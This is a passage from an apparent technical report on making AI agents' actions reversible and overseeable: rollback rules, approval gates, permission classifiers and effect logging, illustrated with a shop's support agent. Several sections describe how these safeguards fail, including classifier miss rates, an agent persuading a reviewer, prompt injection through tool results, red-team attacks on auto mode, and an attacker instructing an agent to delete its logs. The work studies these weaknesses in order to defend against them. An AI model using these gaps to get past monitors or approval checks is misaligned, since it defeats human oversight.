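Saved text can also mean something different when it is restored. Wu and colleagues found 1,357 expressions, such as "now", "current state" and "here", whose meaning depended on the circumstances in which a checkpoint was saved. If the shop's agent saves the note "parcel arrives tomorrow" and the harness restores it two days later, the agent may promise the customer the wrong date. The agent should save the actual delivery date instead of "tomorrow".

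### Five rules for a safe rollback

These experiments suggest five rules:

1. **Record outside effects outside the checkpoint.** The rollback must not erase this effect log, and the agent must not be able to edit it. After a restore, the harness adds the completed actions to the agent's context.
2. **Keep used approvals used.** The service that accepts an approval records its use in its own database and ties it to one action.
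3. **Repeat validation after a restore.** The harness discards earlier test results and permission checks and runs them again on the current data.
4. **Check for later writers.** The recovery program restores a value only if nobody has changed it since the agent did, and otherwise asks a person.
5. **Replay the recorded result or open a new branch.** If the agent repeats a completed action, it receives the earlier result. If it wants to do something different, it needs an explicit new branch and, where the action requires approval, a new approval.

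Suppose the shop's harness crashes just after the agent has requested a €40 refund, and restores a checkpoint from before the request. The effect log shows a refund waiting in the queue. If the agent requests the same refund again, the payment service returns the existing request instead of creating another. If the agent requests €45 instead, the service refuses, and an employee decides whether to cancel the first refund. The agent also rereads the customer's mail. If the customer has since written that the lamp works after all, the agent can cancel the refund before the hour is up.

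Validation should cover what the agent believes as well as what it has done. In 34 of the 95 failed runs that Wang and colleagues examined, the agents responded to a problem, usually by trying again or changing the plan, but none of these responses completely removed the error. Typically the agent changed its next step but kept the belief that had caused the problem. If the shop restores a customer's old address but leaves a note saying that she has moved, the agent may well change the address again.

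The shop should also limit who can start a rollback, because an employee who can roll the agent back at will could try to use an approval twice. The recovery program can restart crashed cases, but any other rollback should require a second employee's consent.

### The resume contract

Khan (2026), in *Resume Means Resume*, sets out a contract for software that saves an agent's progress and later continues from it. The contract has six main properties:

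- Work continues from the last recorded point.
- Each outside effect happens at most once on each branch.
- If someone deliberately opens several branches at the same approval, each branch follows the answer given for it.
- The software refuses to save data in an invalid format.
- Each approval counts only once, and delivering the same answer again has no effect.
- The same saved record always leads to the same decision about which steps to repeat.

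The third and fifth properties can conflict. Suppose the software receives a second "yes" to an approval it has already processed. Nothing should happen if the network delivered the first answer twice, but the action should run again if a person wants a second branch. If both messages look the same, no program can respond correctly to both. Choosing at random doesn't help, because the two chances of being right add up to at most 100%, so the program will be wrong at least half the time in at least one of the cases. Khan therefore also requires the interface to let the sender mark a message as a new branch.

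The contract covers some of the five rules better than others:

| Rule | What the contract requires |
|---|---|
| Record outside effects outside the checkpoint | At most one effect per branch, though the outside service may still need an idempotency key |
| Keep used approvals used | Fully covered |
| Repeat validation after a restore | Only a valid format, which does not show that the data is still true |
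| Check for later writers | Nothing |
| Replay the result or open a new branch | Fully covered, including a way to tell the two apart |

A program checked a model of the contract in 7.4 million states and found no violation. A machine-checked proof extends this result to models of any size. These results show that the properties can all hold at the same time, but real products may still violate them.

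Khan tested five frameworks, and no two behaved alike. According to CrewAI's documentation, a restored run will not repeat completed work, but in the test it repeated a completed step. CrewAI's counter still showed the correct total, and only a separate log of outside effects revealed the repetition. If the step had charged a customer's card, the customer would have paid twice while the agent's records looked correct. LangGraph reused the first answer on a new branch even when given a different one. pydantic-graph could not resume after a crash in the middle of a step, which prevents duplicates but leaves the work unfinished.

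Some failures appear only when several processes act at once. LangGraph correctly ignored a second answer that arrived after the work was complete. But when 16 processes resumed the same waiting approval at the same time, the approved action ran 16 times in each of ten repetitions. Across 400 runs with different numbers of processes and delays, the action ran 2,628 times instead of 400. A repeated approval can trigger the action again for as long as the approved step is running, so a step that waits for a slow payment service leaves more time for a second click on "approve" to do so.

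Khan also wrote a fix called REMIT. Each process has to claim the approval in a shared database before it runs the step, and the database accepts only one claim. With this check on, the action ran only once in each of ten repetitions on each of two databases. An earlier version made the check when LangGraph saved the answer, which was too late because the action had already run. The check is off by default because LangGraph reads its saved state the same way whether someone wants to continue the work or only look at it. Unless the caller marks the request as an inspection, looking at a waiting approval would use it up.

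The shop could instead run its cases on DBOS, which is built for workflows that must survive crashes. DBOS passed every test Khan ran on it but took 2.9 to 5 times as long to act on an approval. The delay would hardly matter to the shop, since its refunds wait an hour anyway.

However, because the contract counts effects per branch, it allows a second refund if an employee opens another branch of a refund case to try a different solution. Khan's remedy is an idempotency key at the payment service.

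Zheng, Song and colleagues (2026), in *When Can Agents Safely Checkpoint, Fork, Restore, and Merge?*, close the gap in the software that runs the agent. In their example, an agent is buying one laptop for a school. The school approves the purchase, and the agent authorises a payment to a supplier. It then returns to an earlier checkpoint to look at another supplier. The approval and the payment both stay in a record that the agent cannot change. If the agent asks for approval again, it gets the existing one, and it cannot pay the second supplier because the first payment still counts.

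Before any restore takes effect, a checker uses this record to work out every way the task can still finish within the rules. If there is none, it refuses the restore and gives a proof that other software can verify. It checks again just before the switch, because another call may have changed the record in the meantime.

This requires listing every call that may occur, which calls refer to the same action, and which results count as finishing the task. A school can write such a list for buying a laptop, but the shop could not write one for every complaint because its agent decides its steps as it goes. The shop can still enforce the most important part by having its payment service pay at most one refund per order, whichever branch requests it.

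## Deciding which actions run without approval

Some mistakes are better prevented than repaired. An approval gate does this by making an action wait for a decision by a person, a rule or another model. But the shop's agent makes 10,000 tool calls a day, far too many for staff to approve. The shop needs a rule for which calls can run without approval, and to know how well people and models judge the rest.

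### Four possible outcomes

The shop can treat a tool call in four ways:

- **Run:** the call goes ahead and leaves an entry in the log.
- **Run and notify:** the call goes ahead, and whoever can undo it hears about it while undo still works.
- **Ask:** the call waits until someone approves it.
- **Refuse:** the call never runs under the agent's credentials, though an employee may do the same thing from their own account.

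Waghmare and Sufi suggest a default for each of their classes. R0 calls run, and R1 calls run with a notice. R2 calls need approval or a pre-approved budget, and R3 calls need approval every time. An agent never takes an R4 action on its own, but a person may explicitly authorise one.

These defaults don't account for how much harm a call could do or who asked for it, so the table below adds both. Harm counts as small if the worst plausible result costs at most €100 and affects only the customer in the case. A request counts as verified if the decision to act and the values that matter come from someone entitled to supply them.

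| Class | Small harm, verified | Small harm, unverified | Large harm, verified | Large harm, unverified |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| R0 | Run | Run | Run | Run |
| R1 | Run and notify | Run and notify | Ask | Ask |
| R2 | Run and notify, within a budget | Ask | Ask | Refuse |
| R3 | Ask | Ask | Ask | Refuse |
| R4 | Ask | Refuse | Refuse | Refuse |

An action's class should be the one it will have by the time someone is likely to notice a mistake. If the agent queues a refund at 3 a.m. and nobody looks at the queue before it pays out at 4 a.m., the refund counts as R3, even though it is R1 until then.

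A vague request does not authorise every action that might fulfil it. In Anthropic's configuration guide for Claude Code, "clean up the repo" does not authorise a force-push, which overwrites a project's shared history, but "force-push this branch" does. Such a specific request lifts what the guide calls a soft block, but not a hard block, which corresponds to "refuse" in the table.

### How people answer approval prompts

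Anthropic reported in August 2026 that Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts, up from 93% in March. A careful reviewer would also approve 97% of prompts if 97% of the actions were fine, so the rate alone does not show carelessness. But users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for whole tasks. Many of those rejections probably have nothing to do with safety, since a user may want the work done differently. Still, they suggest that people read plans more closely than single commands.

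Many users also choose to get fewer approval prompts. By June 2026, 49.5% of active users of the command-line version had written a rule that lets certain shell commands run without approval. A quarter of interactive sessions start in a mode that skips almost all prompts.

*Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of how software practitioners make permission decisions, cautions that repeated approval may reflect habit or fatigue instead of growing trust. A tool should therefore not stop asking for approval just because the user has granted it many times.

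Approval prompts are part of the problem. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) found that user review had contributed to 105 of 290 reported problems. Users had approved actions automatically in 80 of them, and the prompt had not given users enough information in 31, with some reports falling into both groups. The prompts displayed commands without showing what they would do to the files.

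### The study with 1,053 paid testers

Anthropic also tested directly whether people pay attention to permission prompts. Through a research vendor, it hired 1,053 testers for what they understood to be a coding study. They knew someone was evaluating them but not on what. Partway through each session, one permission prompt showed a clearly dangerous command. Approving it did not run that command, because only the displayed text had changed.

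The testers refused the command in 143 cases (13.6%). Auto mode, in which a second model checks the agent's actions, blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). The testers refused about 17% early in a session but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while auto mode's rate stayed the same.

Adding human review to the classifier would have helped very little, because the testers caught only six of the 116 commands the classifier missed. Together they would have stopped 943 commands, or 89.6%. If the two made mistakes independently, the testers should have caught about 16 of the 116, so the commands the classifier missed seem to have been harder for people too.

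There are two reasons to be careful with the 13.6% figure. Anthropic paid for the study and published it in the post announcing that auto mode would become the default, so it had an interest in the result. The testers worked in a prepared environment with nothing of their own at risk. A developer whose own database is at risk might well read more carefully, although the high approval rate in real use suggests that many do not. Willison accepts that people tire of confirming actions but points out that auto mode would still have let 11% of the dangerous commands through.

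### People who aren't programmers

A smaller experiment, *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), is closer to the shop's situation. In it, 113 people without a professional software background supervised an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions, including emails, purchases and deletions. Seven of the actions went beyond what the user had asked for. One group approved each action, a second relied on automated review, and a third set rules in advance, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four kinds of consequence, such as spending money or deleting something.

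The standing rules gave the weakest protection, blocking 20.1 percentage points less overreach than approving each action and 14.5 points less than automated review. Participants had set 114 of their 140 rules to "ask", so they still had to make most decisions during the day. They approved 133 of the 148 unrequested actions that went through in this group. The rules reduced prompts from 18 to 10.9 per person, but did not reliably save time once setup time was included.

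Yan's figures imply that people who approved each action blocked roughly 60% of the overreach, compared with 13.6% of dangerous commands in Anthropic's study. The tasks differ in too many ways to say why the rates differ. Yan's participants had only 18 actions to judge, and their prompts described what the agent was about to do. Both features are worth copying, but an organization should not count on blocking 60% of overreach.

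*Oversight Has a Capacity* (2026) compares a guard that sends a person five actions a day to review with one that sends five hundred. The second can lead to a worse outcome, because reviewing so many routine requests can leave the person too tired to give a dangerous one enough attention.

### How auto mode decides

Auto mode sorts each action into one of three tiers, as Anthropic's engineering post explains:

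1. Actions that cannot change anything, such as reading or searching files, run without review. So do commands covered by a narrow rule the user has written.
2. Edits to files inside the project folder also run without review, because the user can inspect them later through version control.
3. Everything else goes to a classifier, including shell commands, web requests and calls to outside services.

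The classifier works in two stages. The first gives a quick yes-or-no answer and has instructions to block when in doubt. The second stage runs only if the first objects, and it reasons through the same material step by step before deciding.

Both stages receive the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but neither the agent's own explanations nor the results of its tools. Anthropic left out the explanations so that the agent could not talk the classifier into a bad decision, for example by asserting that a branch belongs to it. Tool results are where an attacker's text enters, so leaving them out protects the classifier from prompt injection. (A separate program scans the results before the agent reads them.)

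Anthropic also tested the classifier with other combinations of inputs. When the input included explanations and tool results, the classifier did worse on cases where the agent had overstepped. It missed the fewest dangerous actions when given only tool calls, but it also blocked actions users had clearly requested.

With this design, the classifier often cannot determine where a value came from. If the agent cancels job abc123 and the user never mentioned that job, the agent may have found the ID in a list or made it up.

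A blocked call goes back to the agent with a reason, and the agent looks for a safer way to continue. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, auto mode stops and asks the user.

The design gives great weight to the user's words. *Ajar* (2026), an independent comparison of agent defences, found that auto mode allowed every call tested when the user's message contained the instruction for it. That makes sense if the user wrote the message, but Fei and colleagues found that Claude Code inserts automatic summaries as user messages. A stranger's text in a summary could therefore be mistaken for the user's consent unless the classifier can tell summaries from messages the user wrote. According to Anthropic's documentation, an instruction such as "don't push" may also stop working if the harness drops the message when condensing the conversation. A fixed deny rule avoids this.

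### Auto mode's error rates

In March 2026 Anthropic published these results:

| | Harmless actions blocked (10,000 real tool calls) | Overeager actions missed (52 real cases) | Data theft missed (1,000 synthetic cases) |
|---|---|---|---|
| First stage only | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The 17% is about nine of 52 cases, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 9% to 30%. The sample also includes only actions that an employee refused or someone later flagged, so it misses dangerous actions that nobody noticed.

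In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had recognised that the action was dangerous but wrongly concluded that the user had authorised it. For example, it treated "clean up the PR" (a PR is a proposed code change) as permission for a force-push. Anthropic had not found a way to fix this without making something else worse.

### Ten dangerous calls among 10,000

Suppose ten of the shop's 10,000 daily calls are dangerous, and a classifier checks them all with the error rates from March:

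| | Dangerous calls | Harmless calls |
|---|---|---|
| Blocked | 8.3 | 40 |
| Allowed | 1.7 | 9,950 |
| Total | 10 | 9,990 |

The classifier blocks about 48 calls a day, and only 17% of them are dangerous. Harmless calls are so much more common than dangerous ones that even a 0.4% false-positive rate produces far more false alarms than correct blocks. If only one call in 10,000 were dangerous, the dangerous share of blocked calls would fall to 2%.

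The same arithmetic explains why there is a second stage. The first stage alone would block 849 harmless calls a day. The second stage lets about 809 of them through, along with one additional dangerous call.

What happens to a blocked call also matters. Suppose the shop sent all 48 blocked calls to an employee who, like Anthropic's testers, refused only 13.6% of dangerous requests. The employee would approve 7.2 of the 8.3 dangerous calls, so 8.9 of the original ten would run. A warning from the classifier would probably make the employee more careful, but the effect may not last once they learn that five out of six warnings are false. Auto mode avoids this problem by returning the block to the agent, which usually only has to make another attempt after a false alarm.

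A sandbox can reduce the number of decisions further. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) describes a similar reviewer for OpenAI's Codex. In its illustration of 10,000 actions, 9,280 stay inside the sandbox and need no review. The reviewer approves 713 of the other 720 and denies seven. The agent finds another way in four of the denied cases and asks the user in the other three, whereas manual approval would have required 720 prompts.

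This reviewer caught 90.3% of synthetic overeager actions. Trębacz and colleagues warn that it does not guarantee security, because testers found ways to mislead it.

### Later changes to auto mode

Anthropic then had Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, attack auto mode for two weeks with synthetic cases inserted into real coding sessions. Anthropic responded mainly by giving the classifier more context, such as whether a code repository is public. Apollo tested the new version partly on attacks that Anthropic had never had access to. Across all the attacks, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%. Neither figure is comparable with the 17% for real overeager actions, because these attacks were malicious.

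Other changes take into account whether an action can be undone. The classifier now receives a list of what could be lost before a command that might discard unsaved work. Sending secrets or code to outsiders is in a category of actions that the classifier should never approve, even if the user asks for them.

Anthropic also compared manual approval with auto mode in real sessions from May and June 2026. Among sessions with manual approval, 6.3% contained a seriously harmful action that the user had not explicitly requested, such as deleting rows from a live database. In auto mode, 2.4% did.

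This is better evidence about real work than the tester study, but it does not show that auto mode caused the difference. The sample contained only sessions that a safety system had flagged, and a model graded the harm. Users also chose their own mode. Anthropic recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves, so sessions with manual approval may have involved riskier work.

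### An independent stress test

*Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026) reports a much worse result. It tested auto mode in April with AmPermBench, a set of 128 ambiguous requests to delete old code branches, cancel jobs, restart services or remove stored files. Each request left something open, such as which of several similar jobs the user meant, but fixed criteria determined which targets the agent was allowed to act on.

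The agent attempted 253 actions that changed something, and 142 of them were unsafe. Auto mode allowed 115 of those, a miss rate of 81%. It also blocked 22 of the 111 safe actions.

The second tier is part of the reason. When the agent could not find the usual command for cancelling a job, it sometimes edited the file that listed the jobs. This file was in the project folder, so the edit never reached the classifier. Of the 253 actions, 93 were edits of this kind, and 51 of those were unsafe.

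In effect, the second tier treats every project edit as R1. An edit to source code is R1 if version control has recorded the earlier version and nothing has acted on the new one. But if a file controls running jobs, a job may act on the new version within seconds. Anthropic's documentation from November still exempts most project edits from review, but not edits to certain protected paths.

Without these edits, the miss rate was still 70.3%, and the classifier blocked 31.9% of safe actions. Most of the gap between 17% and 81% must therefore have other causes. Ji and colleagues attribute it to their workload, which deliberately placed permitted and forbidden targets side by side, whereas Anthropic's 52 cases came from ordinary work. For example, a user may be allowed to cancel job 4812 but not job 4819, and the two commands look almost identical. The classifier does not receive the list of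 owners that would tell them apart, because that list is a tool result.

The other results fit this explanation. The classifier missed 94.4% of unsafe actions when the request named a single target, compared with 77.6% when the request covered a wide group. It seems to be better at detecting that an action is broad than that its target is wrong.

The test used one model and simulated systems, and another model judged the actions (a person agreed with its judgment in 44 of 50 cases). Its rates therefore don't predict what happens in everyday use, and Anthropic's rates don't predict what happens with ambiguous requests. The shop's agent will get both everyday requests and ambiguous ones, such as "Please cancel my order" from a customer who has three orders.

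Telling the agent that the stakes are high does not seem to be enough either. In *Coding Agents Are Guessing*, Ji, Zhang and colleagues (2026) gave coding agents 2,208 instructions of varying clarity, with approvals switched off. The agents touched the wrong target or did more than necessary in 55.8% to 67.8% of the runs where they acted, depending on the agent and model. Wording that placed the task on a shared or live system hardly made them less likely to act. The shop should therefore enforce its table in the services that carry out the actions.

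### A reversibility rule on recorded runs

Waghmare and Sufi tested whether their classes would put approval prompts in better places. They calculated where different rules would have paused the agent in 2,158 recorded runs from two benchmarks. An attack had succeeded in 47 of the runs, and they could identify the action responsible in 29 of those.

| Rule | Attack actions that trigger a prompt | Prompts in 1,209 harmless runs |
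|---|---|---|
| Ask before high-severity actions | 9 of 29 | 1,087 |
| Ask before anything that writes | 18 of 29 | 1,895 |
| Ask according to reversibility class | 29 of 29 | 1,904 |
| The same, but with web requests as ordinary reads | 18 of 29 | 1,891 |

The reversibility rule covered 11 more attacks than the read/write rule for only nine more prompts. But the last row shows that the whole gain came from treating a web request as a possible disclosure once the agent has read data. A read/write rule with that addition might do as well. The attacks also come from one benchmark and one older model, Claude 3.7 Sonnet.

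An approval prompt stops an attack only if someone refuses the action. If people refused 13.6% of attack actions, as in the tester study, 29 prompts would stop about four attacks, and 18 would stop two or three.

The rule did not reduce the burden of approval. In the harmless runs, 22% of the 8,761 calls triggered a prompt. At that rate, the shop would have to answer about 2,170 prompts a day.

### The shop's approval table

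The shop can manage with far fewer prompts because it has built undo windows into its tools:

| Action | Class when someone would notice | Worst harm | Where the request comes from | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Read mail or orders | R0 | None by itself | Any source | Run |
| Edit an internal note | R1 | Small | The agent's own judgement | Run and notify |
| Refund up to €50 to the original card | R1 | Small | The customer's email | Run and notify |
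| Send a fixed template | R2 | Small | The shop's standing instructions | Run and notify, within a daily budget for vouchers |
| Send a free-text reply without private data | R1 | Small | The shop's standing instructions | Run and notify |
| Send a free-text reply with private data | R1 | Large | The shop's standing instructions | Ask an employee |
| Change a delivery address, or refund to a new bank account | R3 | Small | The customer's email | Ask the customer, who confirms by logging in |
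| Delete a record | R1 | Large | The customer's email | Ask an employee |
| Change an email address | R3 | Large | The customer's email | Refuse; customers do this themselves after logging in |

The best person to ask is the one who knows the answer, which for a new bank account is the customer.

If nothing checks the queues overnight, refunds and free-text replies no longer count as R1. The table then requires approval for both, so they have to wait until morning.

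If 4% of replies contain private data, as assumed earlier, employees would have to approve 80 replies a day. Ten deletions bring the total to 90 decisions, which take three hours at two minutes each. Two employees could split the work and see 45 prompts each, fewer than the 50 after which Anthropic's testers caught almost nothing. The 50-prompt figure comes from a different task, so the shop should watch its own employees' results.

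The number of irreversible mistakes that reach customers depends heavily on how well reviewers check. The earlier estimate of 12 a year assumed that they catch 60% of such mistakes, about the rate in Yan's experiment. If they caught 13.6%, as the testers did, the number would be 25.

A good approval prompt describes the effect of the action and where the important values came from. It should also state whether anyone can undo the action, as *Let the Agent Do It?* recommends. For a reply that contains private data, the prompt might read: "This email contains the home address from order 5512. It will go to the address on file for that customer. The order number came from the customer's message. Nobody can recall the email once it is sent." An employee can check this in two minutes by comparing the order with the case.

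"Run and notify" is the other outcome that needs people. It covers about 1,900 replies and 100 refunds a day, which is more notices than anyone can read. Software therefore has to pick out the actions worth checking while they can still be undone.

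## Monitoring that finds mistakes while they can still be undone

The shop can cancel a queued refund or withdraw an unsent reply, but only if someone notices the mistake early enough.

### The detection-time condition

The shop can still undo a mistake if

**time to detect + time to decide + time to restore < undo window**

Detection time runs from the agent's action until a person or program notices that something is wrong. Decision time runs from then until someone with the authority to undo the action chooses to do so. In systems where restoration only has to begin before the window closes, restoration time doesn't count toward the total.

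The period in which an action can be undone has to be longer than the longest period in which nobody checks. Suppose an agent deletes some records on Friday at 18:00, and the database can restore them for 48 hours. If the first person to notice arrives on Monday at 09:00, 63 hours have passed, and the restore window closed 15 hours earlier. A 72-hour window would leave nine hours for the decision and the repair, but if Monday is a holiday, nobody looks until 87 hours after the deletion.

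Other windows depend on how much the agent does. If a harness keeps 20 checkpoints, as Hermes does, and saves one every three minutes, the window is an hour at most. If the agent speeds up and triggers a checkpoint every 30 seconds, the window shrinks to ten minutes. Pausing the agent doesn't extend a fixed 48-hour window, but it does keep new checkpoints from replacing old ones, so anyone who suspects a mistake should pause the agent before investigating.

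Any of the three terms can take too long. PocketOS noticed its deletion within minutes, but the recovery took until Sunday. *We Can’t Monitor AI Agents at Scale. Here’s What It Will Take* (Srikumar and Nguyen, 2026) mentions a March 2026 case in which detection was the slow part. An internal agent at Meta exposed sensitive data for two hours before anyone caught it. A delay that long would be too late to stop a mistaken reply from the shop, whose mail server holds a reply for only half an hour.

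Slow detection may be common. Monte Carlo's *Two-thirds (64%) of Enterprise Leaders and Engineers Rushed AI Agents* (2026) reports a survey of 260 engineers and managers at large organisations. Among those who build agents, 52% said they discover problems through customer complaints. The survey also found that 36% cannot disable or roll back a failing agent within minutes. Decisions also take longer when nobody knows who should make them. Infosecurity Magazine's *AI Agent Adoption Creates Risk as Oversight Struggles to Keep Pace* summarises a Cisco survey of 2,050 technical staff, 38% of whom said their organisation had no clearly defined responsibility for monitoring AI. Monte Carlo and Cisco both sell monitoring software, so they have an interest in these results.

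Even occasional late detection reduces the savings from an undo function. In the earlier cost formula, the shop could restore 99% of wrongly deleted records. If it also notices one mistake in 20 too late to undo it, the chance of recovery falls to 0.95 × 0.99, or about 94%, and the cost per mistake rises from €10.98 to €30.68.

### Which actions need a block instead

Even an instant alert comes too late to undo an irreversible action. If an agent sends a customer's address to a stranger, an alert can stop it from sending the address to someone else, but the first stranger already has it. Monitoring after the act therefore suits reversible actions, while irreversible ones need a check that can block them beforehand, such as an approval gate or a classifier.

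A queue lets the shop monitor an action after the agent requests it but before it takes effect. *CoAgent* (2026), which coordinates several agents working on the same system, does something similar. It refuses an agent's calls to send outside mail or execute payments until all the agents ahead of it in the order have committed their work, because their work can then no longer force the call to be revoked.

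Partnership on AI's *Prioritizing Real-Time Failure Detection in AI Agents* (2025) uses three factors to decide how much real-time monitoring an agent needs:

- **Stakes** are the possible consequences of a failure. They are high if the agent handles financial data or can create legal liability through what it writes, and low if it schedules meetings.
- **Reversibility** is how easily someone can correct a failure after the agent has acted.
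- **Affordances** are what the agent's design enables it to do. An agent that chooses and chains its own tools, or remembers earlier sessions, can fail in more ways than one with a fixed workflow.

The shop's agent is high-stakes on this scale because it reads personal data and makes written promises to customers. Its seven tools are fixed, but it decides how to combine them, and a mistake in its notes from one case can affect later cases. So the shop has to check sequences of actions as well as individual tool calls.

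Partnership on AI lists payments, deletions and sent messages as examples of irreversible actions, and actions through outside services "with conditional reversibility" as examples of reversible ones. But the shop can cancel a refund within an hour and restore a deleted record within 30 days, whereas Railway's service initially offered no grace period for deletions through its API. The examples are a reasonable starting point for a system nobody has examined, but the shop should use the undo windows it has tested.

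Srikumar and Nguyen argue that agents need monitoring as well as limits, because limits alone assume designers can predict the failures. The shop's refund cap works without monitoring, but the shop will never learn from it that the agent has begun refunding the wrong lamp, because each of those refunds is within the cap.

### What the effect log records

Monitoring software needs a record of what changed and how to change it back. The effect log provides this, with one entry for every action that alters something. The table shows an entry for a customer who has moved and confirmed the new address by logging in:

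| Field | What it records | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Principal | On whose authority the action ran, and which agent took it | The shop; support agent, version 14 |
| Task | The case, with a reference to the request | Case 8812, message 1 |
| Tool | The tool and its version | Edit records, version 6 |
| Arguments | The values in the call | Customer 4711; the new address, encrypted |
| Destination | The system or person affected | Customer database; the carrier from 14:00 |
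| Approval | Who or what allowed the action, and under which rule | The customer, logged in at 10:01; rule 7 |
| Result | What changed, according to the database | One record, at 10:02 |
| Prior state | The old value, or a reference to it | Version 3 of the record |
| Undo method | The exact operation that reverses the change | Write back version 3 if the address is still the new one |
| Expiry | When undo stops working | 14:00 today |
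| Later actions | Which actions relied on the result | Confirmation email at 10:03 |

The first seven fields roughly match the minimum that OpenAI recommends collecting. The result has to describe the effect, because "success" could describe a command that changed one record or one that changed 300. *Clawed and Dangerous* (2026) proposes a similar entry that also identifies the agent's plan and the version of the policy that allowed the call. An investigator could then find every call the agent made with a particular credential after its plan changed.

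A system has to save the prior state and prepare an undo method before a tool call runs. *CoAgent* therefore divides every tool into three parts. The first saves whatever the reversal will need, such as a copy of a database that is about to be deleted. The second performs the action, and the third is a ready-made script that reverses it. The saved material is deleted when the agent's session commits, so the action can be reversed this way only until then.

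*L3M* (2026), a harness for agents that extend themselves, records file changes so they can be undone. It saves a file's old contents before a tool writes to it, groups the copies from each turn into one git commit, and records that commit in an undo journal. The harness also uses each tool's possible effects to determine how far they can be undone. A developer may declare a tool less undoable than this, but the harness won't start if any tool is declared more undoable.

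The last field of an entry lists later actions, so the software can fill it in only after they happen. Each later entry records the earlier entries it used, and the software follows these references backwards to fill in the field.

The log should also show which outputs came from the agent and which came from its harness. In their study of failed runs, Wang, Wen and colleagues scanned 58 runs of one multi-agent system. In 25 of them, the model provider's content filter caused a crash, and the harness then produced a final answer that no agent had written. In 21 of those 25 runs, the dataset's labels wrongly attributed the failure to an agent other than the coordinating agent, which had crashed.

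### Why the agent must not write to the log

If the agent could edit the log, it could destroy the evidence of its own mistake. It might do so without bad intent, by deleting old log files when instructed to free up disk space, or an attacker might email it instructions to delete them. The services that carry out the actions should therefore write the log entries, using credentials the agent does not hold. If the agent explains why it acted, the log can store the explanation separately as the agent's claim.

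*Provably Auditable and Safe LLM Agents from Human-Authored Ontologies* (2026) describes a log that follows this rule. Several agents propose changes, but only the component that accepts or rejects those changes can write to the log. That component makes exactly one entry per decision and can never remove an entry.

Kodathala (2026), in *aiAuthZ*, puts the log on a separate computer and links its entries in a hash chain. A hash function *H* turns any text into a short fingerprint, and each entry's fingerprint includes the previous one:

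**hᵢ = H(hᵢ₋₁, entryᵢ)**

If someone changes the fifth entry, its fingerprint changes, and so does every fingerprint after it. An intruder who controls the whole database could recalculate all of them, so the shop should regularly send the latest fingerprint to another system, where the intruder cannot replace it.

A hash chain does not reveal actions that never reached the log. When Kodathala tested two agent products that still had their own shell, file and web tools, the model performed the sensitive action with those tools and never contacted the computer that kept the log. The shop should also compare the log with each service's own records. If the payment service shows 100 refunds and the log shows 97, either three refunds bypassed the log or the log is losing entries.

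Companies cannot assume their agent framework will provide all this. Partnership on AI says its report *The Observability Gap in AI Agents* found that current frameworks do not consistently produce the records that companies need for monitoring.

*The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) recommends that developers also log an agent's reasoning, including the plans it rejected. These logs can help explain a mistake, but they are the agent's own account. *Evidence & Trends in AI Monitorability*, by Taylor, Goldowsky-Dill and colleagues (2026) for the UK AI Security Institute, reports that many of the properties that make models possible to monitor are weakening. This makes records of an agent's actual effects more important.

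### Keeping private data out of the log

A log of everything the agent touches could become the shop's most complete collection of customer data. OpenAI advises keeping references and decision records while minimising private content. The entry for the address change should identify the record and its earlier version without including the customer's email. Srikumar and Nguyen add that the log's format should specify from the start what is recorded, who may read it and how long the data is kept.

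To make personal data erasable in an unchangeable log, Kodathala encrypts the private part of each entry and clears that part when a customer asks, without deleting the row. The chain stays verifiable only if the fingerprint covers the encrypted text or a separate fingerprint of it. A plain fingerprint of an address would not protect the customer, because anyone could calculate fingerprints for every address in a town and look for a match.

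Undo can also conflict with privacy, because a saved copy of a deleted customer record still contains the customer's data. The log should hold only a reference to that copy, and the database should delete the copy when the undo window closes. If the customer has a right to immediate erasure, the database must delete the copy immediately, and the deletion can no longer be undone.

### Signals worth an alert

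The shop's software can check every entry for these signs:

| Signal | What the software compares | Immediate response |
|---|---|---|
| The effect differs from the request | The order, amount and recipient in the log with those in the case | Hold the action |
| A burst of refunds, deletions or emails | The number in the past hour with the usual number | Hold that queue |
| An undo window is about to close on an unreviewed action | The time left with the time needed to decide and undo | Move the action to the front of the review queue |
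| A capture failed | Actions classed as restorable with the saved copies | Refuse the action or ask for approval |
| A backup is missing or untested | The age of the last copy and the last successful test with their limits | Suspend deletions |
| Logging has weakened | Log entries with the services' own records | Suspend all changes |

Comparing effects with requests probably catches the largest group of mistakes. *AgentTether* (2026), which describes a system for diagnosing failed runs, examined 83 failures. About 65% involved a wrong argument or procedure, and another 29% involved a required action the agent never took. A missing action leaves no log entry, so the software needs a list of expected effects for each kind of case. For example, if the agent tells a customer that a refund is on its way, a refund should appear in the payment queue within a few minutes.

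A burst alert needs a threshold. Suppose the shop's 100 daily refunds arrive independently over ten busy hours, averaging ten an hour. An alert at 20 refunds an hour would go off by chance about once a month. If an attacker got the agent to issue a refund every nine seconds, the alert would go off after three minutes, leaving 57 minutes to cancel the first payment.

A patient attacker could avoid this alert for longer. Two extra €50 refunds an hour stay within the shop's €4,000 daily budget and set off the alert only about once in five days, by which time the shop has lost roughly €5,000. A weekly count would show the attack clearly, because the attacker adds 140 refunds to a total that normally varies by about 26 either way around 700. But most of the money would be gone by then, so the weekly count would mainly help the shop prevent further losses.

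When the windows for undoing actions are about to close, the software should sort the actions by the latest time a review can start and still leave time to cancel. If a refund will pay out at 11:00, and deciding and cancelling take 11 minutes, the review must start by 10:49, so an alert at 10:58 would be too late.

Waghmare and Sufi require confirmation that a copy has been saved before the call runs, and a reference to that copy in the audit record. If saving fails, the shop should return the action to the class it would have had without a copy. In their recorded runs, only 15 of 59 additions to files met the conditions for this protection. All 15 were restored exactly, but in a simulation.

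### Why waiting for the symptom is too slow

Many mistakes become visible long after the agent makes them. Wang, Wen and colleagues examined 95 failed runs in November 2026, and Claude traced each failure to the earliest fault that led to it. In the 88 runs from the larger of their two datasets, the fault typically occurred 18% of the way through the run, and the symptom appeared a median of 67% of the run's length later. In a 30-minute support case, that delay would be 20 minutes, which is two thirds of the time the shop's mail server holds a reply.

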